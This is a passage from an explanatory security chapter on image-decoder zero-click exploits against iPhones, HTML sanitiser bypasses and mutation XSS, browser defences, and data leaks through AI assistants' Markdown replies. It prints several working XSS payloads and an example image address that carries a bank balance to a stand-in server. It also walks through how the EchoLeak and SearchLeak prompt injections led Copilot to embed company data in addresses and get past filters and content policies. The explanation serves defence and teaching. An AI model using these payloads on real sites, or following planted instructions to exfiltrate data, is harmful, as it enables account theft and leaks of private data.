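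The decoding library, ImageIO, works out a picture's format from its contents and ignores the file name. Any file whose name ended in ".gif" could therefore reach the decoders for more than 20 image formats, some of them obscure and complicated. Beer and Groß estimate that this exposed hundreds of thousands of lines of code.

The picture in this attack reached a decoder without going through BlastDoor, so the attack did not depend on a fault in BlastDoor itself. A sandbox protects only the paths that its designers route through it, and they can easily miss one if a routine is named as though it only copies a file. Checking that the file was a GIF would have blocked this exploit, but not one aimed at a bug in the GIF decoder.

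### A computer made of drawing commands

The PDFs contained images in JBIG2, a format from the late 1990s for compressing black-and-white scans. A JBIG2 file stores the shape of a letter such as "e" once, then lists the places where it appears on the page. It can also store corrections to individual pixels. A JBIG2 decoder is therefore an interpreter that carries out a list of drawing commands.

Apple's decoder counted shapes with a 32-bit counter, which can't go above about 4.3 billion. A crafted file could push the total past this limit, restarting the counter from zero and leaving it on a small number. The decoder then reserved far too little memory and wrote past the end of it. In FORCEDENTRY, the excess data overwrote the decoder's record of the page's height. Later commands could then write to memory far outside the page, much as the crafted BMP files did in Adobe Reader.

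The attackers still had to find the libraries in memory. ASLR had put them at addresses the attackers couldn't know when they wrote the message, and they had to do everything with one file. Exploits against web browsers often solve this with JavaScript, which can search memory and calculate addresses, but JBIG2 has no scripting language.

NSO's developers built a substitute out of the format's corrections. JBIG2 applies these by combining dots with logical operations. AND gives 1 if both inputs are 1, and XOR gives 1 if the inputs differ, so XOR with 1 flips a bit. Together they produce an operation called NAND:

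```
a NAND b = (a AND b) XOR 1
```

Engineers can build any digital circuit from NAND operations alone. FORCEDENTRY used more than 70,000 drawing commands to build a small computer, with registers to hold numbers and circuits to add and compare 64-bit values. This computer ran on the phone while the decoder read the picture, searching memory and working out the addresses. It is a weird machine, made of operations meant for tidying up scanned letters.

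The memory bug let the commands reach memory outside the page, and the format had a rich enough set of commands for the attackers to build a computer from them. A bare bitmap contains no commands, so a similar bug in a bitmap reader would have given the attackers much less to work with.

### An escape through a query language

IMTranscoderAgent had its own sandbox, though a looser one than BlastDoor's. In a second post, published in 2022, Beer and Groß explained how the attackers escaped that sandbox without corrupting any more memory.

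The computer made of drawing commands only made iOS load and run an *expression*. Apple's developers use expressions to search and filter lists, such as finding names that begin with "t". Before 2007, an expression could call only five built-in functions: sum, count, minimum, maximum and average. Apple then extended the language to let expressions call almost any function in the system's libraries. This turned a query language into something close to a general-purpose programming language, with the same kind of reflection that defeated Elasticsearch's filter.

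The attackers next had to get from IMTranscoderAgent into CommCenter, a more privileged program that handles the phone's mobile connection. CommCenter accepted some requests from inside the sandbox, and one had a field declared so loosely that it could hold almost any kind of object. The attackers used that field to send a second expression.

Apple had anticipated this danger, so an expression that arrives from another program stays disabled until the receiving program approves it. But two classes in one of Apple's libraries approved and ran an expression while unpacking it, without checking its contents. The attackers wrapped their expression in these classes, and it ran with CommCenter's rights and downloaded the next part of the attack. Meanwhile, the first expression had deleted the fake GIF to hide the evidence.

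Rewriting CommCenter in Swift would not have prevented this, because every component ran as written. The escape also did not depend on a particular version of iOS, which made it more reliable than most memory exploits. Beer and Groß blame the mechanism that carries objects between programs. Developers must list the functions that another program can call, but the objects passed to those functions vary too much for anyone to review them all. BlastDoor's reply to imagent is much safer in this respect because it contains only named fields of known types.

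Apple fixed the counter in iOS 14.8, released on 13 September 2021. A week later, iOS 15.0 moved all GIF decoding into BlastDoor. For phones that stayed on iOS 14, iOS 14.8.1 limited the image formats that IMTranscoderAgent could decode. iOS 15.1 then weakened the expression language so that expressions could no longer create or destroy objects, and Apple restricted the two classes that had approved expressions automatically.

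### BLASTPASS: an exploit inside BlastDoor

By 2023 NSO had a new zero-click exploit for iMessage. Citizen Lab captured it on the phone of an employee of a civil society organisation based in Washington, DC, and named it BLASTPASS. It worked against iOS 16.6, then the latest version, and Apple released a fix on 7 September. The most detailed account is Beer's *An analysis of the NSO BLASTPASS iMessage exploit*, based on samples he obtained with Amnesty International's help.

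The message carried a pass for Apple's Wallet app, a file that usually holds a boarding pass or ticket. The pass included a logo with a name ending in ".png", but the file was a WebP, a newer picture format. The phone accepted it despite the mismatch, as it had with the fake GIFs.

A compressed WebP picture includes a description of the tables needed to decompress it. The decoder built each table before checking that the description was valid. It had reserved enough memory for any valid table, but an invalid one could run past the end. The decoder did reject the picture, but only after writing one small value in the wrong place. LangSec's rule of full recognition before processing is meant to prevent this kind of error.

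That single value was enough because the attackers had arranged the memory around it. The picture took up only about 1 KB of a 5.5 MB file. Nearly all the rest was in a metadata field that camera makers can use as they like. Apple's software unpacked this field as a structured list, which reserved almost half a million pieces of memory in a pattern that put data worth overwriting where the stray value would land. The pass also contained a second mislabelled picture, which continued the attack after the decoder had stopped processing the first.

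Beer didn't find another computer made of image commands, though he had expected one. The attackers already knew where the libraries were in BlastDoor's memory when they created the file, so they didn't need to search. He thinks they probably learned the addresses through a separate flaw involving HomeKit, Apple's system for controlling household devices. If so, that flaw let them get round the iOS 14 defences against guessing those addresses.

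Researchers first assumed that BLASTPASS had avoided BlastDoor, as FORCEDENTRY had. A post on the Isosceles security blog suggested that iOS decoded pictures inside a Wallet pass in a different program, outside the sandbox. The idea was reasonable because it explained why the attackers had used a pass instead of sending the picture directly. It also seemed to explain why Apple had fixed a second flaw, in Wallet.

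But in Beer's experiments, and in the crash logs he then had from real attacks, the phone decoded the pictures inside BlastDoor. Matthias Frielingsdorf of the security company iVerify lent him an iPhone with iOS 16.6, and Beer attached a debugger to BlastDoor and watched most of the exploit run there. The attackers' code also looked for BlastDoor's connection to imagent, which would make little sense if it were running in another program. Beer concluded that the pass was useful to the attackers because it made the phone decode two pictures in succession, and he guessed that the Wallet flaw was the failure to reject pictures that weren't PNGs.

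This settles where the captured samples ran, but the early hypothesis may still have been right in another respect. In late 2024 Beer received more crash logs, two of which strongly indicate that the same WebP flaw was also reachable in the Messages app itself, outside BlastDoor. Attackers had targeted those phones in November 2023, two months after Apple's fix. The logs record crashes, so they can't show whether an attack by this route succeeded.

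It's also unclear how the attackers escaped from BlastDoor. The last part of their code was encrypted, and it waited for a later iMessage to deliver the key. Beer and Frielingsdorf could not find such a message, but they consider it very likely that the encrypted part contains a sandbox escape. The sandbox did have some openings. The rules that Beer quotes allow contact with three hardware drivers, all related to graphics, whereas the rules Groß described in 2021 forbade all such contact. Apple may have needed to allow these three when it moved image decoding into BlastDoor.

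While waiting for the key, the attackers' code took over the parsing of every message that imagent sent to BlastDoor. Even without escaping the sandbox, code in this position can read incoming messages, and in principle it could alter them before the phone's owner sees them. For example, it might replace the account number in a supplier's message, and imagent would still receive a well-formed text field.

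Beer argues that isolation forces an attacker to use a longer chain of exploits but does not necessarily reduce the code they can attack at the start. Moving the image decoders into BlastDoor, for example, isolated them but did not fix their bugs. For the metadata field, he suggests a size limit or a stricter parser that rejects duplicate entries, of which the BLASTPASS file had many.

### More attacks through pictures

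The same kind of flaw has kept appearing. In 2025 Apple fixed one in its decoder for DNG, a format for unprocessed photographs. A DNG file records how many colour values each pixel has, and the compressed picture inside it records the number again. hackyboiz's *ImageIO* (2025) traces the flaw to a mismatch between the two numbers, which made the decoder write past the end of its memory. LangSec's advice to avoid dependencies between distant parts of a message applies directly here.

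The picture may have reached its targets through a flaw in WhatsApp, according to Quarkslab, a French security company. The flaw let an attacker make someone's phone download material from any web address and process it. The UAE Cyber Security Council attributes it to weak checks on the messages that keep a user's linked devices in sync, and reports that attackers may have combined the two flaws in a zero-click attack on prominent people. *DNGerousLINK*, a talk at the Chaos Computer Club's congress in December 2025, covered zero-click attacks through WhatsApp on both iPhones and Samsung phones. A picture sent through WhatsApp doesn't go through iMessage, so BlastDoor doesn't protect against it.

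People who haven't updated their phones also remain exposed to flaws that Apple has already fixed. Citizen Lab's *Pegasus Spyware Infection of Serbian Pro-Democracy Student Activist* (2026) reports a zero-click infection through iMessage between December 2025 and January 2026. Citizen Lab believes that iOS 18.4.1 blocks the exploit. That version came out in April 2025 (Mascellino, *Pegasus Zero-Click Exploit Infects Serbian Student Activist's iPhone*, 2026), so if Citizen Lab is right, an update available eight months earlier would have stopped the attack.

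Flaws are still coming to light before Apple has a fix. *Apple Patches Zero-Day Linked to 'Extremely Sophisticated Attack'* (Kovacs, 2026), published on 29 September 2026, reported another flaw in CoreGraphics, the library that FORCEDENTRY had exploited five years earlier. Meta's security team had alerted Apple. It is unclear whether the attack linked to the flaw needed a click.

### Memory tags and Lockdown Mode

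Apple can't quickly rewrite all its older code in Swift. ETCentric's *Apple Introduces Major Security Upgrade to Its iPhone 17 Line* quotes Wired as saying that programmers everywhere used memory-unsafe languages for decades. Since September 2025, new iPhones have had hardware that catches many memory errors in the old code while it runs. Apple's *Memory Integrity Enforcement* describes the system on the iPhone 17 and iPhone Air. It gives each piece of memory a secret tag, and a program must present the right tag to use that piece. Neighbouring pieces have different tags, so a decoder that writes past the end of its piece fails the check, and iOS can then stop the program. The system also changes the tag when it reuses memory, which catches use-after-free errors, the type behind the Outlook flaw.

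Apple's engineers tried to adapt real spyware exploits to get past the new protection. Their results show six exploit chains, and they report that they could not rebuild any of the chains they tried, even with new bugs substituted. An overflow that stays within a single piece of memory can still get through, but they consider such bugs extremely rare. The results are impressive, but they come from the company that makes the phone, and real attackers have had only about a year to respond. The Freedom of the Press Foundation, giving an informed opinion rather than test results, considers the feature Apple's best improvement to iPhone security in years.

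Memory tagging wouldn't have stopped FORCEDENTRY's sandbox escape, which used logic bugs and no memory errors. Beer and Groß predicted in 2022 that attackers would turn to logic bugs as memory tagging spread. But memory tagging would probably stop many attacks before the sandbox escape, because an attacker must first take control of a program inside the sandbox, and most known exploits do this by corrupting memory.

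Lockdown Mode, which Apple introduced in 2022, reduces the amount of code that a message can reach. Once a user switches it on, it blocks most types of message attachment and some complex web features, according to MacRumors' *Apple Says No iPhone in Lockdown Mode Has Ever Been Hacked* (2026). A Wallet pass can't exploit a picture decoder if the phone doesn't process the pass. Beer recommends this approach, which protects against memory and logic bugs that nobody has found yet.

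In March 2026 Apple stated that it knew of no successful attack by commercial spyware on a device in Lockdown Mode. MacTrast's *iPhones in Lockdown Mode Have Never Been Hacked* (2026) reports that the head of Amnesty International's security lab told reporters much the same. These statements cover only detected attacks, and spyware often removes its traces, as FORCEDENTRY did. There is also more direct evidence. Particle.news' *Apple Says No Devices in Lockdown Mode Have Been Hacked* reports that Citizen Lab has documented the mode blocking both Pegasus and a rival product called Predator, and that Google's researchers found spyware that stops its attack when it detects the mode. The attacker may be unable to continue or may not want to risk exposing an expensive exploit, but the phone's owner benefits in both cases.

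Demand for this protection is widespread. In August 2026, TechRepublic's *Apple Warns Users in 110 Countries of Mercenary Spyware* reported that Apple had sent a new round of warnings to people it believed attackers had targeted, with Lockdown Mode among the recommended precautions. The protection is probably worth losing most attachments for an activist or a reporter, but the loss would be a nuisance for the clerk, whose suppliers send invoices as files.

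## HTML sanitisers: cleaning text before a browser displays it

The clerk's accounting system is a website, and suppliers can add a note to each invoice. When the clerk opens an invoice, the browser receives a single string of HTML, with the supplier's note in the middle of text written by the site's developers. HTML marks up text with *tags*, such as `<b>` for bold, and the browser can't distinguish the supplier's tags from the developers'. If the note contains a `<script>` tag, the browser may run the script as part of the accounting site.

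Security engineers call this attack *cross-site scripting*, or XSS. The script can do whatever the site's own code can do, so it can read what the clerk types, change the amounts on the page or approve a payment in the clerk's name. The browser's sandbox keeps the script away from the clerk's files, but it doesn't protect the money the clerk handles through the website. According to Mozilla's *Goodbye innerHTML, Hello setHTML* (2026), XSS has ranked among the top three web vulnerabilities for nearly a decade.

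### Escaping and sanitising

If suppliers don't need formatting, the site can *escape* their notes, replacing each character that has a special meaning in HTML with a code that displays it. `<script>` becomes `&lt;script&gt;`, and the clerk sees the word "script" in angle brackets. *Parse Me, Baby, One More Time* (Klein and Johns, 2024) recommends this wherever users should have no influence on the markup.

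The right way to escape text depends on where it will end up. *Dancer in the Dark* (2025), which studies attacks on pages the attacker can't see, distinguishes between text inserted into ordinary HTML, into a web address and into JavaScript code. Suppose the site turns each supplier's homepage address into a link. The address `javascript:steal()` contains no angle brackets, so HTML escaping leaves it unchanged, and the browser runs it as code when the clerk clicks the link.

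Sites sanitise HTML when they want to keep some of the markup, such as bold type and links. Some developers write their own denylists for this. In a talk with the same title as the paper, Klein recommended using a sanitiser with a real HTML parser instead, and he did the study to test whether that advice was good enough.

### How DOMPurify cleans a note

DOMPurify is a free sanitiser, begun in February 2014 and maintained by the security company Cure53. Suppose a supplier submits this note:

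```
Now <b>overdue</b>: <a href="https://pay.example/41" onclick="steal()">pay here</a><script>steal()</script>
```

DOMPurify first has a parser turn the string into a tree. Each tag becomes an *element*, and the settings inside a tag, such as `href`, become its *attributes*:

```
"Now "
b
    "overdue"
": "
a       href = https://pay.example/41
        onclick = steal()                 ← delete
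    "pay here"
script                                    ← delete
    "steal()"
```

It then walks through the tree and compares every element and attribute with its allowlists. The elements `b` and `a` are on the list, but `script` isn't, so DOMPurify deletes it along with its contents. It also deletes `onclick`, which would run a program when the clerk clicked the link. The `href` attribute has to pass another check, on the type of address. An `https:` address is acceptable, while a `javascript:` address is not. Finally, DOMPurify writes the remaining tree out as a new string:

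```
Now <b>overdue</b>: <a href="https://pay.example/41">pay here</a>
```

The site usually inserts this string into the page by assigning it to the `innerHTML` property. The browser then parses the string and displays the result.

### A bug that needed two parses

DOMPurify checks one tree, and the browser then builds another from the cleaned string. The two are usually identical, but the HTML specification warns that a tree may change when a program writes it out and parses it again. One reason is that browsers repair faulty HTML instead of rejecting it. For example, if a `div` appears directly inside a table, the browser moves it in front of the table. In *mutation XSS*, an attacker writes markup that is harmless in the first tree but becomes executable code in the second.

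Bentkowski (2020), in *Mutation XSS via namespace confusion*, published this exploit against DOMPurify:

```
<form><math><mtext></form><form><mglyph><style></math><img src onerror=alert(1)>
```

The harmful part is the picture at the end. It has no source, so it fails to load, and the browser runs the program in its `onerror` attribute. Everything before the picture makes DOMPurify parse it as text.

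The disguise relies on how browsers parse forms. Forms can't normally contain other forms, so the browser ignores a second `<form>` tag while a form is open. But the early `</form>` clears the parser's record of the first form without closing it, so the second form ends up inside the first.

The other oddity concerns `style`. In ordinary HTML, a `style` element can contain only text. In MathML, a language for formulas that web pages can embed, it can contain more tags. The element around it, `mglyph`, belongs to MathML if it sits directly inside `mtext`. Here the second form comes between them, so the parser treats both `mglyph` and `style` as ordinary HTML:

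```
form
  math
    mtext
      form
        mglyph                  HTML
          style                 HTML, so its contents are text
            "</math><img src onerror=alert(1)>"
```

Every element in this tree is on DOMPurify's allowlist, and the picture is only text. DOMPurify therefore deletes nothing and writes out a tidy string, with one form neatly inside the other and no early `</form>`. When the browser parses that string, it ignores the second form, and `mglyph` lands directly inside `mtext`:

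```
form
  math
    mtext
      mglyph                    MathML
        style                   MathML, so its contents are markup
  img   onerror = alert(1)      ← runs
```

The `</math>` tag now closes the formula, the picture becomes a real picture, and its program runs.

The Daily Swig's *Security flaw introduced through the serialization of foreign content* dates the fix, DOMPurify 2.0.16, to 18 September 2020. Within days, researchers found another bypass with a similar cause, and GitHub Advisory Database's *Cross-site Scripting in dompurify* (2020) lists every version before 2.0.17 as vulnerable. Fastmail, an email company that uses DOMPurify, paid Bentkowski $250 for his discovery.

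He then wrote a broader fix, which Bentkowski explains in *Helping secure DOMPurify*. DOMPurify now checks which language each element belongs to and deletes elements that appear in the wrong one. An `mglyph` in ordinary HTML suggests something is wrong, so DOMPurify deletes it. Bentkowski also advised sites to have DOMPurify return the cleaned tree instead of a string, because the browser can insert a tree without parsing it again.

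### Eleven sanitisers and 12 million inputs

When DOMPurify runs in a browser, the tree it cleans and the tree the browser displays at least come from the same parser. Many sites instead clean text on their servers, using a separately written parser that may differ from the browser's.

Klein and Johns tested 11 server-side sanitisers in five programming languages. They wrote a program called MutaGen, which generated 12 million different inputs by wrapping a few simple exploits in markup that is hard to parse. They ran the inputs through the sanitisers and loaded any output that still contained the exploit's code in Chromium, Firefox and WebKit, the engine behind Safari. The whole process took 14.5 days.

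The researchers bypassed nine of the 11 sanitisers. Six failed in their default configuration, and the other three failed only after the researchers allowed more tags. Allowing one or two extra tags was usually enough, and many sites would allow some anyway. According to Klein, the tested libraries had over a billion downloads combined.

Some of the misreadings were simple. An HTML comment begins with `<!--` and normally ends with `-->`, but browsers also accept `--!>`. Three sanitisers didn't know this, so they read the following line as one long comment:

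```
<!-- c--!><img src=x onerror=f()>-->
```

The browser ends the comment at `--!>` and then displays the picture, which runs the program.

The researchers also counted 19,843 inputs that were harmless until a sanitiser processed them. In one case, DOMPurify was running on a server with an old version of a parser called jsdom. The input contained an escaped picture tag, which DOMPurify correctly treated as text. But jsdom decoded the text while writing it out, so the output contained a working picture tag.

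To measure how well each sanitiser understood HTML, Klein and Johns compared its trees with the browsers' trees. They listed the path to every leaf in both trees, then divided the number of shared paths by the number that occurred in either:

```
similarity = shared paths / (paths in tree 1 + paths in tree 2 − shared paths)
```

A score of 1 means identical trees. The scores in Chrome ranged from 0.15 for HtmlRuleSanitizer to 0.94 for rgrove/sanitize, a Ruby library. These inputs were designed to be difficult, so the scores would probably be higher for ordinary notes.

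A good score did not guarantee safety. The two sanitisers that withstood the test, sanitize-html and loofah, scored only about 0.4 and 0.2. They were safe because they always escape text in their output, so if they mistake a tag for text, the browser also receives it as text. Klein and Johns estimate that escaping text this way would have prevented all but two of the bypasses they list. Such a sanitiser may still misread honest notes and damage them, but a clerk can tolerate damage such as a missing heading.

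A sanitiser bypass can let an attacker steal passwords. Klein found one in HotCRP, a system that academic conferences use to review papers. Several leading security conferences share its login data. He showed that an attacker could set up a conference page with a hidden script, log visitors out and record their passwords when they logged back in.

Even a sanitiser that followed the HTML specification perfectly could fail, because browsers don't always follow it. Firefox handled embedded formulas and drawings differently from Chrome, so some inputs that were harmless in Chrome ran in Firefox. A sanitiser on a server usually can't account for the reader's browser. Klein and Johns conclude that server-side sanitising cannot be both accurate and secure.

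### Text that moves after cleaning

A site can also undo a sanitiser's work by changing the output afterwards, a mistake that Sonar's *mXSS Explained* calls "desanitization". OSV's *GHSA-h8r8-wccr-v5f2* (2026), a security advisory from March 2026, gives an example in which DOMPurify receives a picture with a strange description:

```
<img src=x alt="</xmp><img src=x onerror=alert('expoc')>">
```

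The second picture is only part of the first one's description, so the markup is harmless. But the site then puts the cleaned string inside `<xmp>`, an obsolete element whose contents are plain text. Quotation marks have no special meaning there, so the `</xmp>` in the description ends the element, and the browser treats the second picture as a separate element.

DOMPurify 3.3.2 fixed the problem. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-0540* (2026), a closely related entry from Spain's cybersecurity institute, attributes the vulnerability to five elements missing from one of DOMPurify's checks. The advisory also attributes it to sites that move cleaned text into a new context, and recommends sanitising text as close as possible to where it will appear.

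Browser makers have also made this kind of attack harder. web.dev's *New to the web platform in June* (2025) reports that Chrome 138 and Firefox 140 escape angle brackets inside attributes when they write out HTML. If DOMPurify runs in one of these browsers, a `</xmp>` in a picture's description should therefore no longer close an element. But the advisory's demonstration ran DOMPurify on a server, where the browser change has no effect.

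Researchers are still finding other bugs. OSV's July entry, *CVE-2026-49978* (2026), describes how DOMPurify could skip some content when cleaning a tree in place, leaving a script inside it intact. Version 3.4.7 fixed this. Asking for a tree instead of a string avoids the second parse, but scripts can still get through in any element the sanitiser doesn't check.

### One parse with setHTML

Browser developers have built a sanitiser into the browser. Braun helped write the design and explains it in *Why the Sanitizer API is just setHTML()*. He first wanted a function that returned a clean string, as DOMPurify does, but the browser would have had to parse that string again, perhaps inside a different element. Braun describes the usual combination of DOMPurify and `innerHTML` as an accidental weird machine for producing mutation attacks.

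The final version is a method called `setHTML`. A developer writes `note.setHTML(text)`, where `note` is the part of the page that will hold the supplier's text. The browser parses the text according to the rules for that part of the page, removes whatever isn't allowed and inserts the rest. It never writes the result out as a string, so the second parse that Bentkowski's form relies on doesn't happen. The method also returns nothing, which keeps developers from moving the result somewhere else.

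Another advantage, according to Klein and Johns, is that a browser's parser and sanitiser ship together and usually update automatically, whereas somebody often has to install each new version of a server library.

The default settings are strict. In Mozilla's example, `setHTML` keeps a heading but removes the picture inside it and the program attached to the picture. Removing pictures can be useful in itself, because a remote image can leak private data from an AI assistant's reply. Developers can supply their own lists if the defaults are too strict or too loose.

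### Limiting the damage from a missed script

A large site may have hundreds of places that insert HTML, and one unsanitised assignment to `innerHTML` is enough for an attack. *Trusted Types* makes the browser reject ordinary strings at these places. Code must pass each string through a policy that the site's developers have approved, so a reviewer can concentrate on the policies. According to Mozilla, a strict site can allow `setHTML` and block the unsafe methods.

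A site whose policy uses a separate sanitiser still depends on that sanitiser. Klein and Johns quote a Google report on the adoption of Trusted Types that traced more than half of the root causes of XSS in browser-side code to bugs in HTML sanitisers.

A *content security policy* (CSP) can help after a sanitiser has failed. The server sends the browser a list of rules about what a page may load and run. One rule can require every script written directly into the page to carry a *nonce*, a random value that the server chooses afresh each time:

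```
Content-Security-Policy: script-src 'self' 'nonce-rAnd0m'

<script nonce="rAnd0m">showTotal()</script>      runs
<script>steal()</script>                         blocked
```

A supplier who wrote a note last week can't know today's nonce. The same policy blocks code in attributes such as `onerror`, so it would have stopped Bentkowski's picture from running code. The policy doesn't help if the site puts the supplier's text inside a script that already has the nonce.

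CSP is powerful, but few sites use it well. Mozilla, which began work on it in 2009, admits that it requires major changes to existing sites and continuous expert review. *Context-Auditor* (2022) reports that most web applications don't deploy it properly. Klein and Johns cite third-party code as an obstacle, because it often relies on scripts that a strict policy blocks.

All the main browsers support CSP, but support for the newer protections varies:

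| Protection | Chrome and Edge | Firefox | Safari |
|---|---|---|---|
| Content security policy | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Trusted Types | Since version 83 | Since version 148, according to Mozilla | Since version 26.0 |
| `setHTML` | Since version 146 | Since version 148 | No |

Firefox 148, released on 24 February 2026, was the first browser to ship the standard version of `setHTML`. Web Platform DX's *Sanitizer API* lists Chrome and Edge as lacking the method, but web.dev's *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API* lists support from version 146. Google runs web.dev and makes Chrome, so its figure is probably right. Sources also differ on Trusted Types in Firefox 148. Can I use's *Trusted Types for DOM manipulation* lists it as disabled by default, while Mozilla's announcement presents it as supported.

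For now, a site with readers on Safari needs a fallback such as DOMPurify, though it can use `setHTML` in browsers that support it.

### The checker and the consumer must agree

The program that checks an input and the program that uses it must parse it the same way. Otherwise, the check applies to something the user never receives. `setHTML` meets this requirement by parsing the input once and inserting the same tree that it checked.

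Other systems can't easily combine the two jobs. Mail filters, for example, usually run on a server, while the mail program runs on the clerk's computer. *Email Smuggling with Differential Fuzzing of MIME Parsers* (Andarzian, Meyers and Poll, 2025) compares how the two kinds of program parse the same message. In one of its examples, a mail program displays a single message as two emails, which might let an attacker hide the second from the filter.

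Web firewalls, which inspect requests before they reach a website, have the same weakness. *WAFFLED* (2025) tests them by changing everything in a request except the attack. It looks for changes that confuse the firewall's parser but not the website's, so that the firewall misses an attack it might otherwise recognise.

LangSec's remedy is a simpler format, but browser makers can't easily simplify HTML. Klein and Johns note that faulty pages are still common, so a browser that rejected them would fail to display much of the web.

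### A fake login request in clean HTML

Suppose every program reads the supplier's note identically, and the sanitiser makes no mistakes. This note still gets through:

```
<b>Your session has expired.</b> To view this invoice, please
<a href="https://accounts-login.example">sign in again</a>.
```

The request contains a bold sentence and an ordinary link, both of which the site is meant to allow. The clerk sees it on the genuine accounting site, with the correct address at the top of the browser. The link leads to a copy of the login page, where a thief collects the clerk's password.

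DOMPurify's allowlist included forms in 2020, as Bentkowski's exploit showed. If a site allows forms and input boxes in notes, a malicious supplier could put a convincing password box directly under the invoice, without needing another page.

The site can remove forms and links from its allowlist, or escape the whole note, but the supplier can still write "Please email your password to our support team", which contains no markup. A box around each note labelled "Written by the supplier" would at least show the clerk that the request did not come from the accounting system.

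## EchoLeak and hidden characters: displaying an assistant's reply

The clerk can ask the office's AI assistant to summarise the supplier's note instead of reading it. Even if the company that built the assistant is trustworthy, the supplier wrote part of what the model reads and can therefore influence what it writes. The web page that displays the summary should handle it as untrusted content, just like the note itself. OWASP, a non-profit that publishes guidance on software security, compares trusting a model's output to giving users indirect access to extra functions in *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*.

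The summary can also do harm that the note can't, because the assistant may have access to company secrets that the supplier doesn't, such as contracts or the bank balance. Its reply can combine those secrets with the supplier's instructions. If displaying the reply sends a request to an outside server, that request can include the secrets.

### How a picture's address carries data

AI assistants usually format their replies in Markdown, a simple notation in which asterisks mark bold type and brackets mark links. Here is part of a reply with a link and a picture:

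```
**Overdue:** [invoice 41](https://pay.example/41)
![logo](https://pictures.example/logo.png)
```

A program converts this to HTML for the browser:

```
<strong>Overdue:</strong> <a href="https://pay.example/41">invoice 41</a>
<img src="https://pictures.example/logo.png" alt="logo">
```

The browser contacts `pay.example` only if the clerk clicks the link, but it normally requests the picture as soon as the page displays it. A web address can end in a *query string*, a question mark followed by information for the server, such as the size of picture to send. Suppose hidden text in the supplier's note has made the model put the company's bank balance there:

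```
honest:     https://pictures.example/logo.png?size=small
altered:    https://pictures.example/logo.png?balance=18250
```

The server receives the whole address and can log it. It then returns a real logo, or a transparent picture one pixel wide, and the clerk notices nothing. This needs no script, so an HTML sanitiser that permits pictures will let it through.

Quarkslab's *From Prompt to Pwned* describes how easily this gap can arise. During a security test, the company's researchers gave a chatbot the Markdown for a picture and told it to include the picture in its reply. The chatbot copied the Markdown, and the page displayed the picture. The picture was a harmless icon, but the page would have fetched one from an attacker's server in the same way.

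### EchoLeak: an email that Copilot read

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their organisation's emails, files and chats. In January 2025, researchers at the security company Aim Security told Microsoft how an outsider could steal data from it with a single email. They called the attack EchoLeak, and its official identifier is CVE-2025-32711. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) explains how it worked.

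The victim didn't have to open the email. It stayed in the mailbox, and when the victim asked Copilot a question, Copilot searched for relevant passages and gave them to the model with the question. The attacker needed the search to return the malicious email. Ravia assumed that the search engine represents each passage as a point in a space of meanings and retrieves the passages whose points are nearest to the question. The researchers therefore wrote a long email with many sections, each presented as a guide to a common subject, such as parental or other leave, and repeated their instructions in each section. An employee who asked about any of these subjects might trigger the attack.

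The instructions told the model to find the most sensitive information it had been given and build it into a web address. Four protections should have made this difficult:

| Protection | Intended effect | Gap |
|---|---|---|
| Injection detector | Keeps malicious instructions away from the model | The email addressed its instructions to a human reader and never mentioned AI |
| Link filter | Removes outside links and pictures from the reply | It missed one of Markdown's notations for them |
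| Content security policy | Stops the browser loading pictures from unapproved servers | An approved Microsoft service would fetch other addresses on request |
| Source references | Show the user which documents the reply drew on | The email asked the reader not to refer to it |

Like many HTML sanitisers, Copilot's link filter failed because it missed syntax that the program displaying the reply accepted. Markdown lets a writer put a link's address next to its text or list it separately, like a footnote, and the filter detected only the first form. A filter that ran after the conversion to HTML would have found an ordinary link or picture in either case.

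After bypassing the link filter, the researchers could steal data if the victim clicked a link. A picture would remove the need for a click, but the content security policy allowed pictures only from a list of more than two dozen addresses, mostly Microsoft's. The researchers searched these for a service that would pass a request on. They first found one in SharePoint, Microsoft's document-sharing system, but it worked only if the victim accepted an invitation. They then found a preview service in Teams, Microsoft's workplace chat program, that required nothing from the victim. The browser requested a picture from Teams, and Teams then requested the attacker's address, which contained the stolen data.

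An allowlist of servers is safe only if no server on it forwards data anywhere outside the list. In *server-side request forgery*, an attacker makes a server send requests on their behalf. In EchoLeak, this technique let an attacker send company data out through a trusted Microsoft address.

Microsoft gave the flaw a severity score of 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5, according to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026). Microsoft's advisory of 11 June 2025, reproduced in exploitDog's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), states that Microsoft had already fully fixed the problem, that customers didn't need to do anything, and that nobody had exploited it. Neither the advisory nor Ravia explains which of the gaps Microsoft closed, and customers couldn't inspect the fix because it was on Microsoft's servers.

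Ravia, whose company was developing a product to detect such attacks, presents EchoLeak as the first case of a new kind of attack, in which an outsider's text makes a model use an insider's data. Willison, in a blog post with the same title as Ravia's, calls it an extended variant of leaks already seen in a dozen products. Copilot was one of them. *Trust No AI* (2024) describes a flaw, fixed in July 2024, that let an email make Copilot search the inbox and put what it found into a link. EchoLeak was new in that it got past several protections without the user clicking anything.

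Willison blames a combination he calls the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to an attacker's text, and a way to send data out. The last is usually the easiest to remove, because an assistant that can't read emails from outside or search internal files is much less useful.

### SearchLeak: a sanitiser that ran too late

A year after Microsoft announced the fix for EchoLeak, the security company Varonis disclosed another leak in Copilot, in its Enterprise Search feature. The attack, known as SearchLeak or CVE-2026-42824, began when the victim clicked a link to Microsoft's own website. According to The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox*, it could take emails, calendar entries and files without the victim typing anything.

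Varonis's account, carried by the Cloud Security Alliance, describes three weaknesses. The link contained a search query, which Copilot treated as an instruction to the model. The model's reply contained a picture, which the browser requested before the sanitiser had cleaned the reply. The content security policy allowed requests to Microsoft's search engine, Bing, which could be made to fetch the attacker's address. Bing was already on the list of approved servers that Ravia published in 2025.

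Even if the sanitiser had recognised every dangerous tag, it could still have failed by running too late. Once the browser has sent a request for a picture, removing the picture from the page doesn't recover the data sent with that request. A program should clean the reply before any of it reaches the browser, even when the reply appears a few words at a time.

Microsoft has fixed SearchLeak. Expert Insights' *Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Let One Click Exfiltrate Emails, MFA Codes* (2026) reports that Varonis considered it critical, while Microsoft scored it 6.5 out of 10, partly because it needed a click. The link went to a genuine Microsoft address, which many employees have learned to trust, so needing a click may not have been much of an obstacle. OECD's *Microsoft Copilot Vulnerability Exposed Sensitive Data via AI Prompt Injection* (2026) records another flaw found by Varonis, which Microsoft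 patched in August 2026. It also used a crafted web address to run a prompt without the user's consent.

### Closing the way out

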